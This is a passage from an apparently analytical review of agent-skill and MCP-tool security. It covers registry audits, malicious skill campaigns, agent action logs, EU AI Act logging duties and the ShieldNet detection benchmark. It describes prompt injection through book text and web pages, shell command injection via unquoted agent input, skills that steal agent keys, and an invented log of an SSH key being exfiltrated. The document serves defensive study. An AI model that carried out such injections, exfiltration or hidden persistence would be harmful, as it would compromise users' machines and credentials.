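2. They traced the flow of data through the skills' own Python and JavaScript code without running it. The software looked for a path from a source (input that the agent supplies) to a sink (a call that runs a command or evaluates code) with no effective check in between. In the travel skill, `city` is the source and `os.system` is the sink.
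3. They searched for instructions to download a script and run it immediately, and for code that prints passwords or keys, because the model reads what a skill prints.
4. One researcher reviewed all 3,428 cases from the four main detectors by hand, and a second checked samples. This took about two person-months.
5. They tried to exploit 40 of the flagged cases in a sandbox, and then ran 200 skills with a live agent.

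The review showed how often each detector was right. Precision is the number of confirmed cases divided by the number flagged:

| What the detector flagged | Flagged | Confirmed | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| "Download and run" instruction in an installation section | 202 | 192 | 95.0% |
| The same instruction anywhere in `SKILL.md` | 727 | 445 | 61.2% |
| Flawed library that the skill loads when it runs | 1,419 | 627 | 44.2% |
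| Unchecked path from agent input to a command or code | 848 | 315 | 37.1% |
| Password or key printed to the output | 433 | 22 | 5.1% |

A download command under the heading "Install" is easy to interpret. A printed variable called `token` is harder, because it may hold a real key, a masked preview or just the key's name, and the detector couldn't distinguish between these.

The researchers also tried having a language model review the 848 data-flow cases. One version raised precision to 60.0% but discarded almost a tenth of the real flaws. Another reached 66.5% but discarded more than a third. Human reviewers had trouble with these cases too. When the second researcher labelled all 848 independently, the agreement score was 0.645, where 1 is perfect agreement and 0 is the level expected by chance. The researchers disagreed mainly about whether the agent or the person running it sets certain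 values, so the figure of 315 depends partly on how those values are classified.

### Old flaws in the libraries

The scanner could determine exact versions for 3,128 of the 3,188 skills. Of these, 1,555 (49.7%, although the paper prints 49.6%) depended on at least one version with a known flaw. They make up only 3.2% of the registry, because most skills declare no libraries. About 70% of the skills with an npm manifest had no lock file, so the scan left them out, and nobody knows whether they are better or worse than the skills it covered.

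Skill authors chose only 22.8% of the flawed versions. The rest were transitive dependencies in lock files, or versions that the scanner selected because the author gave only a library's name. The scanner's selections don't seem to have inflated the result, since counting only exact versions and lock files gives 50.7%.

Most of the flaws were already public when the author published the skill. Of the 1,555 skills, 1,217 (78.3%) had at least one such flaw, or 57.1% if one counts only pinned versions. These flaws had typically been public for almost two years, and a fixed version nearly always existed. On npm, by contrast, a library's flaws usually come to light after a project has adopted it.

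Copied package lists explain much of this. With one command, a developer can list every Python package on a computer and save the list as a skill's requirements, including packages the skill never uses. Five authors who did this account for 85.8% of the 1,350 flawed versions that Python skills pinned exactly. One author's list, copied into 40 skills, accounts for 1,092 of them.

After six months, 88.7% of the flaws that the researchers could recheck were still there. Skill authors had upgraded or removed the library in only 1.7% of cases, although more than half of the affected skills had a new version by then.

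### Which library flaws an agent can reach

An advisory usually concerns one function in a library. For example, an image library may have a flaw in a function that evaluates formulas, but a skill that only resizes photographs never calls that function. Here, a flaw is "reachable" if input from the agent can get to the flawed function in the copy of the library that the skill loads.

The 1,555 skills had 21,012 combinations of a skill and a known flaw. Most of them concerned libraries that the skill doesn't load at all:

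| How the skill uses the flawed library | Combinations |
|---|---|
| Declares it but never loads it | 9,239 |
| Uses it only during development | 5,220 |
| Has it only in test files | 1,414 |
| Loads it when the skill runs | 5,139 |

The researchers followed the remaining paths by hand and found a reachable flaw in 47 skills, or 3.0% of the 1,555 flagged. (The precision table gives the number flagged as 1,419, which would make it 3.3%.) Most of these flaws were mild. In 15 of the 47 skills, the library `requests` could leak a password, but only if the user's machine has a particular password file. In others, the flaw could crash or hang the skill. Only five had a more dangerous flaw, such as one that lets an attacker run code or read files outside the intended folder.

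The sandbox results support the same conclusion, but only weakly. The researchers tried to exploit 14 library flaws through the agent and failed each time. By the earlier formula for clean runs, 14 failures out of 14 would still be compatible with a success rate of up to 19%, and the researchers hadn't chosen the cases at random. One of the flaws, in a web server library, did let an attacker crash the server by connecting to it directly. The 3.0% figure excludes routes that bypass the agent.

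### Flaws in the skills' own code

Flaws in the skills' own scripts were far easier to exploit than flaws in libraries. In the sandbox, 21 of 22 exploits worked from start to finish. The other targeted a database query and failed because the skill checked the input and rejected it. A skill's script receives the agent's input directly, so an attacker doesn't need the skill to call a particular function deep inside a library.

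One confirmed case was a reading assistant that sends passages from an e-book to a language model, requests a short program to find the chapters, and runs whatever the model returns. An attacker could hide an instruction in the book's text, and the model might include the attacker's code in its answer. The skill would then run that code with access to the user's keys. A functional test with an ordinary book would pass because the skill would find the chapters correctly.

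The researchers chose cases to cover different types of flaw, so 21 out of 22 is not an estimate of the rate across the registry. A test program also fed the malicious input straight to the skill, so the result doesn't show how often a real agent would pass such input along.

### What happened with a live agent

The researchers drew a random sample of 200 skills that the data-flow detector had flagged, balanced by programming language. They ran them with an agent based on gpt-4o-mini, a small OpenAI model from 2024. The attack was a harmless command that left a marker in a file. The outside content contained this command in all six trials of each skill, and in three of them it also included an instruction for the agent to pass the command on unchanged.

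The command ran in 97 of the 200 skills (48.5%), usually because of how the agent wrote its command line rather than a flaw in the skill. In 95 of the 97, the agent had copied the malicious text into the command line without quotation marks, so the shell, the program that interprets typed commands, executed it before the skill started. The manual review had found no real flaw in 56 of the 97 skills.

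The researchers then repeated the 97 attacks with a different tool. The agent had to name a program and list its arguments separately instead of typing a line into a shell, so the text `$(command)` reached the skill as plain characters. The attack worked in 10 skills (5.0% of the original 200), compared with 92 when the researchers repeated it with the shell. All 10 had confirmed flaws of their own.

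The larger of these two problems is in the program that runs the agent, so an audit of the skills can't find it. The people who maintain that program can fix most of the problem by replacing the shell tool, without changing any skill.

The percentages may not carry over to current agents. In a small pilot, the larger gpt-4o refused inputs that were obviously code, although the researchers expect it would still accept a value that looks like an ordinary web address or date. The 5.0% may also be too low, because another 18 skills failed only because a library was missing from the test machine.

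### Deciding what to fix first

Suppose a company has 1,000 skills with flawed libraries, in the same proportions as on ClawHub:

| Condition | Skills remaining |
|---|---|
| A declared library has a known flaw | 1,000 |
| The skill loads that library when it runs | about 400 |
| Agent input can reach the flawed function | about 30 |
| The flaw is of one of the more dangerous types | about 3 |

If a reviewer needs 20 minutes per skill (an invented figure), checking all 1,000 takes 333 hours, or about 11 hours for each reachable flaw. Spending the same time on 1,000 data-flow alerts would confirm about 370 flaws, or one every 54 minutes. Li and colleagues therefore advise registries to prioritize flaws in the skills' own code over library alerts, and to discard alerts about libraries that a skill never loads. Checking declared versions at publication would also help, since most of the known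 flaws are already public by then.

Treating the other 970 skills as safe would be a mistake, because a skill's next version may call the flawed function, and nobody will repeat the reachability analysis unless something prompts them to. For many libraries the analysis isn't worth doing anyway, because installing the fixed version takes less time than proving the old one harmless.

Malicious releases also need separate treatment. A company that discards every alert about an unused library would discard one about LiteLLM 1.82.8, which ran its malware even in programs that never used LiteLLM. Li and colleagues excluded three advisories about malicious releases from their review, so the 3.0% doesn't apply to such advisories.

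Fixing one type of problem also leaves most of the others in place. The researchers confirmed that 381 skills had a reachable library flaw, an exploitable flaw in their own code or a leaked secret. Only three of those skills had more than one type of problem.

### Malicious skills on ClawHub

The study excluded malicious skills. The researchers classed a skill as malware if it showed at least two of eight signs, such as secrecy instructions or code that sends data to an unrelated server. Only one flagged skill met this rule, and the registry removed it. But the detectors were designed to find accidental flaws, so the result is not evidence that the rest of ClawHub was free of malware.

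Security firms had already found a lot of malware in skills. Koi (2026), which also reported the `postmark-mcp` theft, audited all 2,857 skills then on ClawHub and found 341 malicious ones, 335 of them from a single campaign that it named ClawHavoc. Those skills had professional-looking documentation with instructions, under "Prerequisites", to install another program first. On a Mac, that program was Atomic Stealer, commercial malware that steals passwords and cryptocurrency wallets. The Hacker News reports that anyone with a GitHub account at least one week old could publish a skill.

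Later counts vary a lot, and not all of them are about ClawHub:

| Count | Skills examined | Malicious | Share |
|---|---|---|---|
| Koi, about 1 February 2026 | 2,857 on ClawHub | 341 | 11.9% |
| Koi, 16 February 2026 | over 10,700 on ClawHub | 824 | under 8% |
| Zhao and colleagues, 20 April 2026 | 66,157 on ClawHub | 627 | 0.9% |
| Liu and colleagues, January 2026 | 98,380 on two other registries | 157 | 0.16% |

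In *From Instructions to Exploits*, Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2026) used their own scanner to narrow their copy of ClawHub to 2,473 candidates, ran these in isolation and then reviewed the evidence by hand. Liu, Chen and colleagues (2026) used a similar method on skills.rest and skillsmp.com in the peer-reviewed study *Do Not Mention This to the User*. The 48,682 skills in the March audit probably also included several hundred malicious ones, since ClawHub still had 627 in April.

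The percentages may have fallen because the registry grew after a few accounts had uploaded most of the malicious skills, not because attackers lost interest. Two publishers were responsible for 88% of the cases that Zhao and colleagues confirmed. *MalSkillBench* (Guo, Jia and colleagues, 2026) collected 703 malicious skills from ClawHub, 81% of them from two accounts. The percentage of skills that are malicious is therefore a poor measure of how many attackers there were, or of a user's chance of installing something malicious.

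Totals also change as skills are removed from the registry. By 15 July, only 23 of the 627 were still identifiable there. *MalSkillBench* includes deleted skills recovered from old copies, so a count of the live registry would have missed some of its skills. The security firm Antiy had attributed at least 1,184 malicious skills to twelve accounts by 5 February, according to *Towards Secure Agent Skills* (2026). That is more than Koi reported eleven days later, but the two firms may have counted copies or deleted skills differently.

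Counting copies can greatly inflate the number of malicious skills. Yang, Ying and colleagues (2026), in *Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs*, removed identical copies, which reduced the 703 skills to 193. They then judged each skill author's apparent intent and confirmed 148 as malicious. The 157 skills from the peer-reviewed study contained no identical copies, but only 95 met the same test for malicious intent. The others looked harmless, risky without being malicious, or too ambiguous to classify. *Technical Report* (2026) confirmed 76 malicious skills by hand in an older copy of ClawHub. That figure counts republished copies separately and leaves out flagged skills that there hadn't been time to review, so it isn't a total either.

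Automatic warnings are an even worse basis for a count. NVIDIA's scanner, one of the scanners ClawHub uses, warns against installing 45.8% of the skills that Yang, Ying and colleagues checked. *After the Party* (Xiong and Zhang, 2026) reports that three scanners gave conflicting results for 23,702 of 61,990 ClawHub skills, or 38%.

### Why an advisory scan would have missed them

An advisory scanner would probably miss Koi's 341 skills, though nobody appears to have run one on them. The ClawHavoc skills told people to download a file from GitHub or paste a script from a web page. The scanner doesn't read such instructions, and the skills did not otherwise name the malicious program in a form it could match with an advisory. The Windows download was also in a password-protected archive, which kept antivirus scanners from scanning its contents.

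Two of the six skills outside the main campaign hid the attack in their own code. They were search tools for the betting site Polymarket, and Koi found the malicious code around line 180 of an otherwise working program. That code gave the attacker control of the machine during an ordinary search, and the program then fetched the results. The attack could have worked even if every library was up to date and had no known flaws.

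Data-flow analysis like that used in the March audit would probably have missed that line too. It detects outside input that reaches a dangerous call, but the attacker had written the whole command into the program, so no input from the agent flowed into the call. A simpler search for any code that downloads and runs a script would have found the line, but it would also have flagged legitimate installers.

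The sixth of these skills, `rankaj`, was presented as a weather tool. It read the file where the agent stores its keys and sent the contents to an outside address. The file and the address were fixed in the code, so again no agent input reached a command. To recognise this as theft, a reviewer or scanner has to compare what the skill does with its stated purpose and check whether a weather tool needs the agent's keys.

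## What an action log records

An action log can show behaviour that a dependency audit misses, but how much it shows depends on which program writes it. For example, the agent's own log could not include the recipient that the `postmark-mcp` server added.

### The fields of a tool-call record

OpenTelemetry is an open-source project that publishes a common format for the records that programs keep of their own work. The basic record is a span, which describes one operation and has a start time, an end time and identifiers that link it to related spans. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* defines these fields for a tool call:

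| Field | What it contains | Requirement |
|---|---|---|
| `gen_ai.operation.name` | `execute_tool` | Required |
| `error.type` | The kind of error | Required if the call failed |
| `gen_ai.tool.name` | The tool's name | Recommended |
| `gen_ai.tool.call.id` | An identifier for this call | Recommended if available |
| `gen_ai.tool.description` | The tool's description | Recommended if available |
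| `gen_ai.tool.type` | For example, a function or a data store | Recommended if available |
| `gen_ai.tool.call.arguments` | The inputs that the model supplied | Opt-in |
| `gen_ai.tool.call.result` | What the tool returned | Opt-in |

Software records opt-in fields only if someone turns them on, so a default log can show that an agent called `send_email` at 14:03 without showing the recipient or the reply.

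The full list of tool definitions that the model received is also opt-in, and OpenTelemetry recommends against recording it by default because it can be large. The description field is a partial substitute. In the Deadbugz case, it could have captured the altered text, but only if the agent had called one of the altered tools again. No field records the tool's version or a hash of its code, so a clean release and a malicious one can produce identical records.

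Many companies also keep only a sample of their spans to save storage. That works well for measuring speed, but an investigator may need a span that the company discarded.

OpenTelemetry's conventions for generative AI are still changing. Greptime (2026), a database vendor, lists changes in every release from 1.37 to 1.41. Version 1.37 renamed the field for the model's provider, but OpenTelemetry says existing software should keep using its old version of the conventions by default. A company with several agents may therefore have to search for the same information under two names. The conventions have since moved to their own repository, where they are still labeled "Development", according to TrueFoundry, another vendor.

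### One call in two logs

Suppose a user asks an agent to summarise `report.txt`, and the agent calls a tool on a compromised local MCP server. The tool writes the summary, but it also reads the user's private SSH key and sends it to a stranger. With the opt-in fields switched on, the agent's log might contain this invented record:

```
span name    execute_tool summarize_file
start        14:03:07.120
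end          14:03:07.910
tool name    summarize_file
call id      call_8f2a
arguments    {"path": "/home/ana/report.txt"}
result       "Sales rose by 4% in the third quarter..."
```

Everything in this record is true, and nothing in it looks unusual. A log of the machine's processes, files and connections during the same period would look different:

| Time | Process | Event |
|---|---|---|
| 14:03:07.124 | 4127 (MCP server) | Opens `/home/ana/report.txt` |
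| 14:03:07.131 | 4127 | Opens `/home/ana/.ssh/id_ed25519` |
| 14:03:07.140 | 4127 | Connects to 203.0.113.50, port 443 |
| 14:03:07.262 | 4127 | Sends 1,904 bytes |

The event at 07.131 is suspicious because summarising a report doesn't require an SSH key. The connection is harder to judge, since a legitimate tool might send the report to a language model to summarise. The host-side log shows how many bytes the process sent but not what they contained, so it can't prove that the key left the machine, but Ana should assume that it did.

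The host-side log is not enough by itself either. If Ana had asked the agent to upload code to GitHub, opening an SSH key and then a connection would have been normal. An investigator needs to know what the agent requested as well as what the machine did. *ExecWeave* (Wong and Chen, 2026) notes that either record can mislead on its own. An agent's log may contain a command that never ran, and the operating system may show a process without revealing which agent or tool call started it.

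In *Agent-Warden*, Cui, Gu and colleagues (2026) compared the two kinds of record on the same task. An agent started a script that wrote a file and renamed it, and an unrelated program on the machine later read that file. Langfuse, a popular service for recording what agents do, logged the agent's own steps but not the file operations or the unrelated program. The researchers' host-side recorder reconstructed the whole chain in all 30 runs of each of its two versions on two types of computer. The researchers designed the task to produce this chain, so this result shows that the recorder works as intended, not how it would perform on unfamiliar attacks. The recorder doesn't log network connections, so it would have missed the connection to the stranger in Ana's case.

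Host-side logging has to run on the machine where the tool runs. If the MCP server is remote, a log on Ana's computer would record only the connection to that server.

### How AgentSight joins the two views

Zheng, Yu and colleagues (2025), in *AgentSight*, built a recorder that combines the agent's requests with their effects on the machine. It uses the kernel, the core of the operating system, which handles every request by a program to open a file, start another program or connect to a network. A Linux feature called eBPF lets an administrator run small, pre-checked programs inside the kernel without changing the agent. AgentSight works in four steps:

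1. It attaches to the encryption library that the agent uses and copies the messages to and from the model while they are unencrypted.
2. It records when the agent's process, or any process descended from it, starts a program, opens a file or makes a connection.
3. It links these events to the model's replies. The signals are descent from the agent's process, timing (within 100 to 500 milliseconds of a reply) and matching text, such as a file name that appears in both.
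4. It gives the linked events to a second language model, which judges whether they fit the task.

In Ana's case, the MCP server is a descendant process of the agent application, so AgentSight would record the server opening the key. The key's path never appeared in the model's reply, which might help the second model detect the problem. But if Ana took ten seconds to approve the call, the events would fall outside the time window, and AgentSight would have to link them using the other two signals.

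Zheng and colleagues tested AgentSight on one attack. They asked an agent to build a program whose instructions led to a web page with a hidden prompt. The prompt made the agent send a system file to an outside server. AgentSight recorded 521 events and merged them into 37, and the second model rated the result as a likely attack. The other two tests covered an agent stuck in a loop and a team of six agents that blocked one another's work.

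This is weak evidence that the approach can detect compromised tools. In the test, the agent itself ran the command that stole the file, so the theft probably also appeared in the agent's messages. The researchers did not test a tool that steals data inside its own code, and they did not report how often the second model raises false alarms.

### Delayed effects, and the cost of recording them

A malicious tool can also schedule the theft for later. *AgentLoupe* (Bao, Liu and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an agent that adds an entry to cron, the Linux program that runs tasks on a schedule. An hour later, cron starts a script that gives an attacker control of the machine. The script isn't a descendant of the agent's process, and an hour is far longer than AgentSight's time window.

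The recorder, AgentLoupe, numbers each exchange with the model and attaches that number to any file the agent then writes. If another program opens the file later, that program inherits the number. In a test of the cron attack, AgentLoupe traced the attacker's connection back to the original request. It also traced an instruction that was planted in a file during one session and followed in a later one.

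Bao and colleagues infer from AgentSight's design that it would miss both attacks, and list a direct comparison as future work. They also haven't measured how often AgentLoupe attaches a number to an unrelated event. Such errors could become a problem on a busy machine, where many programs read the same files.

Both teams measured how much longer similar tasks took with recording switched on:

| Task | AgentSight, measured by its developers | AgentSight, measured by Bao and colleagues | AgentLoupe |
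|---|---|---|---|
| Understanding a code repository | 3.4% | 4.5% | 4.5% |
| Writing code | 4.9% | 2.5% | 8.0% |
| Compiling a program | 0.4% | 1.7% | 7.7% |
| Mean | 2.9% | 2.9% | 6.7% |

The means for AgentSight are identical partly by luck, since the teams used different machines and models and ran each task only three or five times. Still, a slowdown of a few per cent would be acceptable for most agents, which spend much of their time waiting for the model.

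These recorders run on Linux, while many people use agents on Windows or Mac laptops. Wong and Chen's ExecWeave includes a recorder designed for all three systems. It checks at intervals what is running instead of receiving every event from the kernel, so it can miss anything that starts and finishes between two checks, as the theft of Ana's key might. It also slows tasks much more than the Linux-only recorders do, and in tests on Linux it increased the running time of three tasks by 62% to 409%.

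### Making changes to a log visible

A local tool usually has the user's permissions, so it may be able to edit a log that the agent keeps in the user's folder. A hash chain makes such edits visible. Each log entry gets a hash computed from its own contents and the previous entry's hash:

hᵢ = H(hᵢ₋₁ || eᵢ)

Here eᵢ is entry number i, H is a hash function such as SHA-256, and || means the two pieces are joined before hashing. The first entry has no previous hash, so it uses a fixed starting value, such as the word "GENESIS" in the working example in *Audit Trails for Accountability in Large Language Models* (2026).

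Suppose Ana's log holds four entries, and the malicious tool changes entry 2 to hide that it opened the key. An auditor recomputes the hashes from the beginning (shortened and invented here):

| Entry | Original event | Stored hash | Hash recomputed after the edit |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Opens `report.txt` | 3f9a | 3f9a |
| 2 | Opens the SSH key | c21e | 80b7 |
| 3 | Connects to 203.0.113.50 | 5d04 | e61f |
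| 4 | Sends 1,904 bytes | a978 | 1b3c |

The hashes stop matching at entry 2. But the formula contains no secret, so the tool could also replace the stored hashes with the recomputed ones, and the auditor would find nothing wrong. The tool could also delete entries 2 to 4, because a shorter chain is still valid.

To detect either change, the auditor needs a copy of the latest hash, a978, from somewhere the tool can't write. *aiAuthZ* (2026), a system for controlling what agents may do, lets operators copy the latest hash to storage that nobody can overwrite. *Agent Flight Recorder* (Bindschaedler, Botha and Siebenbrunner, 2026) publishes its hash on a blockchain, so that two companies in a dispute don't have to agree on who keeps it. The system added 48 microseconds per event, and publishing one hash for every 100 events cost $2.30 per 100,000 events. It detected all the edits, deletions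 and reorderings in tests on artificial agent workloads.

An attacker can still rewrite entries written since the last published hash. If the agent publishes a hash every 100 events, Ana's four entries could all fall between two hashes, since the theft took a fraction of a second. Sending each entry to another machine immediately would leave less time to rewrite it. *Secure Audit Logs to Support Computer Forensics* (Schneier and Kelsey, 1999) describes a method that protects entries written before an attacker takes over a machine. No such method can guarantee that entries the machine writes after the takeover are true.

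### Events that nobody recorded

A hash chain protects only the entries it contains. If Ana's agent keeps a perfect chain of its tool calls, the chain will contain the call to `summarize_file` but nothing about the SSH key, and every hash will still match. Bindschaedler and colleagues explicitly exclude completeness from their system's goals. Entries can also go missing without an attack. Zhao, Hoang and Shoaib report in *Rethinking Tamper-Evident Logging* (2025) that existing tamper-evident systems lose a lot of data when a machine is very busy.

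Finding a missing entry requires a second record from a different source. *Auditable Claims about AI Agents* (Yue Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes an invented firm that claims a person approves every email its agent sends to outsiders. The agent's log shows a confirmation for one email, and the mail gateway's record shows that the email went out. But the server that issues permissions has no record of an approval for it, so the claim is false. With only the agent's log, an auditor might have accepted the confirmation as proof.

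The comparison works better if a program does it. In *Hearsay* (2026), the researchers routed the traffic between an agent and its model through a separate logger that the agent's software couldn't alter. People or programs that read this second log answered questions about the run no better than before, and most of what they cited from it was the agent's own words. The logger can establish that the model wrote "I only read the report", but not that the statement was true.

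### What EU law requires

The European Union's AI Act requires logs for AI systems that it classifies as high-risk. An amendment in force since 27 July 2026 postponed these duties, by 16 months for the systems listed in Annex III, according to the National Law Review:

| High-risk systems | Examples | Duties apply from |
|---|---|---|
| Stand-alone systems listed in Annex III | Employment, education, credit assessment, law enforcement | 2 December 2027 |
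| Systems in products under EU safety law (Annex I) | Medical devices | 2 August 2028 |

An agent that ranks job applicants would normally fall in the Annex III group. One that sends invoices or writes code generally would not, so these articles wouldn't require its owner to keep logs.

Three articles divide the work:

- **Article 12** concerns the system's design. It must "technically allow for the automatic recording of events" throughout its life. Mishcon de Reya's *Article 12 Record-Keeping* reproduces the purposes: to identify situations in which the system may present a risk or undergo a substantial modification, to support monitoring after it goes on the market, and to let the organisations that use it monitor its operation.
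- **Article 19** requires the provider, usually the company that developed the system, to keep the automatic logs that are under its control. The period must suit the system's purpose and be at least six months, unless other laws say otherwise.
- **Article 26** puts the same minimum on deployers, the organisations that use the system, for the logs under their control.

Keeping logs for six months would have left enough time to investigate the cloned Paperclip skills, which stayed on the registry for about three weeks after turning malicious. Postmark keeps messages for only 45 days by default. But when a third party runs a remote MCP server, the provider and the deployer might have no control over its log.

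None of the three articles explicitly requires records of processes, files or network connections. Article 12 specifies what the log must contain only for remote biometric identification. The Art of Service's *EU AI Act EUAI-Art.12* summarises the required contents as the period of each use, the database searched, the input that led to a match and the people who verified it. For everything else, what must be logged depends on the purposes above.

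One could argue that those purposes sometimes require host-side records. If a tool secretly copies applicants' CVs to a stranger, the system presents a risk that its tool-call log may not reveal. One could also argue the opposite, because Article 12 covers events in the AI system, which may not include a third-party tool's internal operations. As Yue Zhao and colleagues note, Article 12 doesn't specify which records would settle a particular claim. *EU AI Act Article 12 and the Interaction-Trace Gap* (2026) also argues that logs of inputs, outputs and tool calls are insufficient, but the evidence it finds missing is about how people delegate to the system and oversee it. The three articles don't require hash chains either.

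### Investigation and privacy

A good log can make recovery from a theft much easier. Ana's host-side log shows which key the tool opened, so she can replace that key first. If the log covers the whole time she used the tool, she may not need to replace every password on the machine. Her employer can search other computers' logs for the address 203.0.113.50 to find out who else had the tool.

The log does not stop the theft, which took about a seventh of a second. *A Black Box for Agentic Processes* (2026), a proposal for tamper-evident agent records, leaves prevention to measures such as access control, sandboxing and monitoring.

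Logs can also leak private data. If Ana asks for a summary of a letter from her doctor, the opt-in result field puts her medical details in the log, and more people may have access to the log than to the letter. LiteLLM suspects that the attackers in October found engineers' GitHub tokens in this kind of log. AgentSight collects even more because it copies the agent's whole conversation with the model. If the second model runs at an outside company, some of that material may go there too.

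By default, OpenTelemetry records no instructions, inputs or outputs. For production systems with sensitive data, it recommends storing this content separately and putting only a reference in the span, so that engineers investigating a slow tool don't automatically see private messages. Security and privacy then conflict less, since file names and addresses in the host-side log were enough to reveal the problem in Ana's case. These can be sensitive too, because a file name may mention an illness or a job application.

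Any change to the data in a hash chain breaks the hashes, so *aiAuthZ* chains a hash of the content instead of the content itself. An operator can then erase the content after the retention period, and an auditor can still verify the chain. Erasure is less effective for short, predictable data. Anyone with the hash of a phone number can try every possible number until one matches, unless the system mixes a secret into the calculation.

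## Scanners, action logs and network monitoring tested on the same tools

*ShieldNet* (Yuan, Chen and colleagues, 2026) tested several checks on the same set of tampered tools. Separate incidents can't show which check works best, because each involved a different tool and different defences. Scanners caught few of the tampered tools, as did language models that read the agent's log, while the researchers' own network monitor caught nearly all of them. But the test favoured network monitoring in several ways. Two authors also list an affiliation with Virtue AI, an AI security company.

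### How the researchers tampered with real tools

The test set, SC-Inject-Bench, contains 984 tools from 109 real MCP servers. (Another table in the paper gives 1,105 tools and 122 servers.) The researchers built it in four steps:

1. They took attack techniques from MITRE ATT&CK, a public catalogue of what attackers do. They kept 29 that worked in a test environment and left a recognisable pattern in network traffic, such as sending stolen data to cloud storage or searching for other machines on the network.
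2. A coding agent found the code behind each tool and inserted a script that carried out one of the attacks. The tool's definition and its normal output stayed the same.
3. A language model wrote several ordinary requests for each tool, and an agent carried them out.
4. The researchers recorded the network traffic. They kept a malicious example only if the agent had called the tool and the traffic contained a marker signal, such as a ping, which each script sent to prove that it had run.

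This produced 19,961 combinations of server, tool and technique, including clean versions. In one example, a user asks for the local time in Kolkata. The tool returns it correctly, but the inserted script also sends dozens of requests to another device on the network to copy its configuration. In the earlier notation, the tool produces the correct output o with the wrong side effects Δ.

### How ShieldNet works

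ShieldNet records the traffic during a tool call and classifies it in three stages.

The first is interception. Web traffic is normally encrypted between a program and its destination. ShieldNet routes it through a proxy on the user's machine, which decrypts it, reads it and encrypts it again before passing it on. Some applications use a newer protocol called QUIC that would bypass the proxy, so ShieldNet blocks QUIC to make those applications fall back to an ordinary connection. ShieldNet also records the raw network packets, because many attacks don't use the web.

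ShieldNet then turns the recording into a list of events in order of time. For the Kolkata request, the list looks roughly like this:

```
22:58:45  web request    agent to model provider
22:58:45  web reply      model asks for get_current_time
          SNMP request   172.25.24.12 to 172.25.24.3
          SNMP reply     172.25.24.3 to 172.25.24.12
          ... dozens more SNMP requests and replies ...
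          ping           172.25.24.12 to 172.25.24.3
22:59:01  web request    agent to model provider
```

SNMP is a protocol for managing network equipment, and a clock has no use for it.

Finally, a small language model, Qwen3-0.6B, labels the list as benign or identifies the attack. The researchers trained it on about 6,000 labelled examples. It identified the Kolkata attack correctly. GPT-4.1, a much larger model, classified the same list as harmless because the conversation looked normal.

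For live use, ShieldNet checks the latest 100 events after every 50 new packets and raises an alarm if they look malicious, but it doesn't block the traffic. The researchers demonstrated this mode with Claude Code but gave no error rates for it.

### The results, and what F1 hides

The main score in the study is F1, which combines precision (the share of flagged items that are malicious) with recall (the share of malicious items that the detector flags):

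F1 = 2 × precision × recall / (precision + recall)

A perfect detector scores 1. The last column below is an estimate of recall, calculated from the two published figures.

| Method | F1 | False positive rate | Tampered tools caught (estimate) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cisco's scanner, before use | 0.029 | 0.9% | 1% |
| Invariant Labs' scanner, before use | 0.164 | 6.8% | 9% |
| Ramparts, another scanner, before use | 0.172 | 12.4% | 9% |
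| GPT-5.2 reading tool inputs and outputs | 0.027 | 1.3% | 1% |
| GPT-4.1 reading tool inputs and outputs | 0.051 | 2.2% | 3% |
| Suricata, a conventional network monitor | 0.062 | 0% | 3% |
| GPT-5.2 reading network events | 0.838 | 26.7% | 73% |
| GPT-4.1 reading network events | 0.908 | 34.4% | 85% |
| ShieldNet | 0.998 | 2.2% | over 99% |

Ramparts flagged clean tools slightly more often than tampered ones. The two language models that read inputs and outputs flagged both kinds about equally often, as expected, because the researchers had deliberately kept the inputs and outputs normal.

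The high F1 scores are less impressive than they look. Safe-NID, another network monitor in the test, flagged every single tool and still scored 0.974. If a share m of the items is malicious, a detector that flags everything has a precision of m and a recall of 1, so

F1 = 2m / (1 + m)

Setting this to 0.974 gives m ≈ 0.95, so about 95% of the test items were malicious. This fits the size of the test set, because one clean version of each tool would make 984 of the 19,961 combinations clean, or 4.9%. With so few clean items, false alarms barely lower the score.

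A high F1 can hide many false alarms. In the test without decryption, ShieldNet's F1 was still 0.977 even though it flagged 89.6% of the clean tools, often because it misclassified the agent's encrypted traffic as data theft. When the researchers also removed the event list and gave the model raw packets, F1 fell to 0.829, partly because long recordings no longer fitted into the model's input.

ShieldNet's false positive rate is therefore more informative than its F1. For individual recordings it was 0.8%, with an F1 of 0.995. The 2.2% in the table is higher because one flagged recording was enough to mark a tool as malicious. If false alarms were independent, the share of clean tools flagged after n calls would be

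1 − 0.992ⁿ

This share reaches 2.2% after about three calls and 55% after 100. In practice, false alarms probably cluster on a few unusual tools, so the share would rise more slowly. But a tool in daily use still has many more chances to trigger a false alarm than it had in the test.

ShieldNet added 21% to the normal interaction time. Language models that read inputs and outputs added about 11%, and those that read network events added 32% to 40%.

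### How the test favoured network monitoring

The choice of attacks determined much of the outcome. Every attack had to be visible on the network, and every tool had to look normal in its definition and output. A test set of tools with malicious definitions but clean code, such as those in the Deadbugz case, could have reversed the ranking.

The marker signal is a more serious concern because every malicious script sent one, and clean tools would not be expected to. Yuan and colleagues don't mention removing these signals before training or testing, and the published Kolkata recording contains a ping. The model could have learned to treat a ping as evidence of an attack, which would not help it detect attacks that don't send one.

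Two results suggest that ShieldNet did not rely only on the ping. It could usually name the technique, which it could not have identified from a marker that was the same in every script. Its false positive rate also rose when the researchers turned decryption off, even though pings remain readable without decryption.

ShieldNet scored between 0.949 and 0.982 on three attack techniques that the researchers held out of the training data. They credit this to the model having learned what clean traffic looks like, but these attacks also contained markers, so a model that had learned to detect pings would score well too. The lowest score was for commands hidden in web traffic, which is closer to how real thieves send data than a burst of SNMP requests. ShieldNet missed an estimated 6% of those attacks.

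The addresses in the Kolkata recording are another possible clue. The attack ran between two addresses in a laboratory network, while the agent used an address in a different range. The model receives these addresses as input, so it could have learned to recognise the laboratory network. Retraining ShieldNet on recordings without markers and with scrambled addresses would test both explanations.

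Ramparts, one of the scanners, scored 0.172 across all tools but 0.000 on both the kinds of server used in training and the kinds held out. Those two groups should together cover the whole set, so the scores seem inconsistent. No independent team appears to have rerun the comparison.

### What scanners find when the code is in view

*MCP-DPT* (2026), a review of defences, reports that Invariant Labs' scanner, MCP-Scan, reads configurations and tool metadata. It may therefore never have read the inserted code, so the poor results for scanners don't show that reading code is useless.

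In *MalTool*, Hu, Jia and colleagues (2026) tested scanners on a similar set of tampered tools. They inserted malicious functions into 5,727 real Python tools, covering 13 kinds of harm. They ran 130 by hand, and all still did their advertised job while carrying out the attack. Most of the harms, such as deleting a file, need no network connection.

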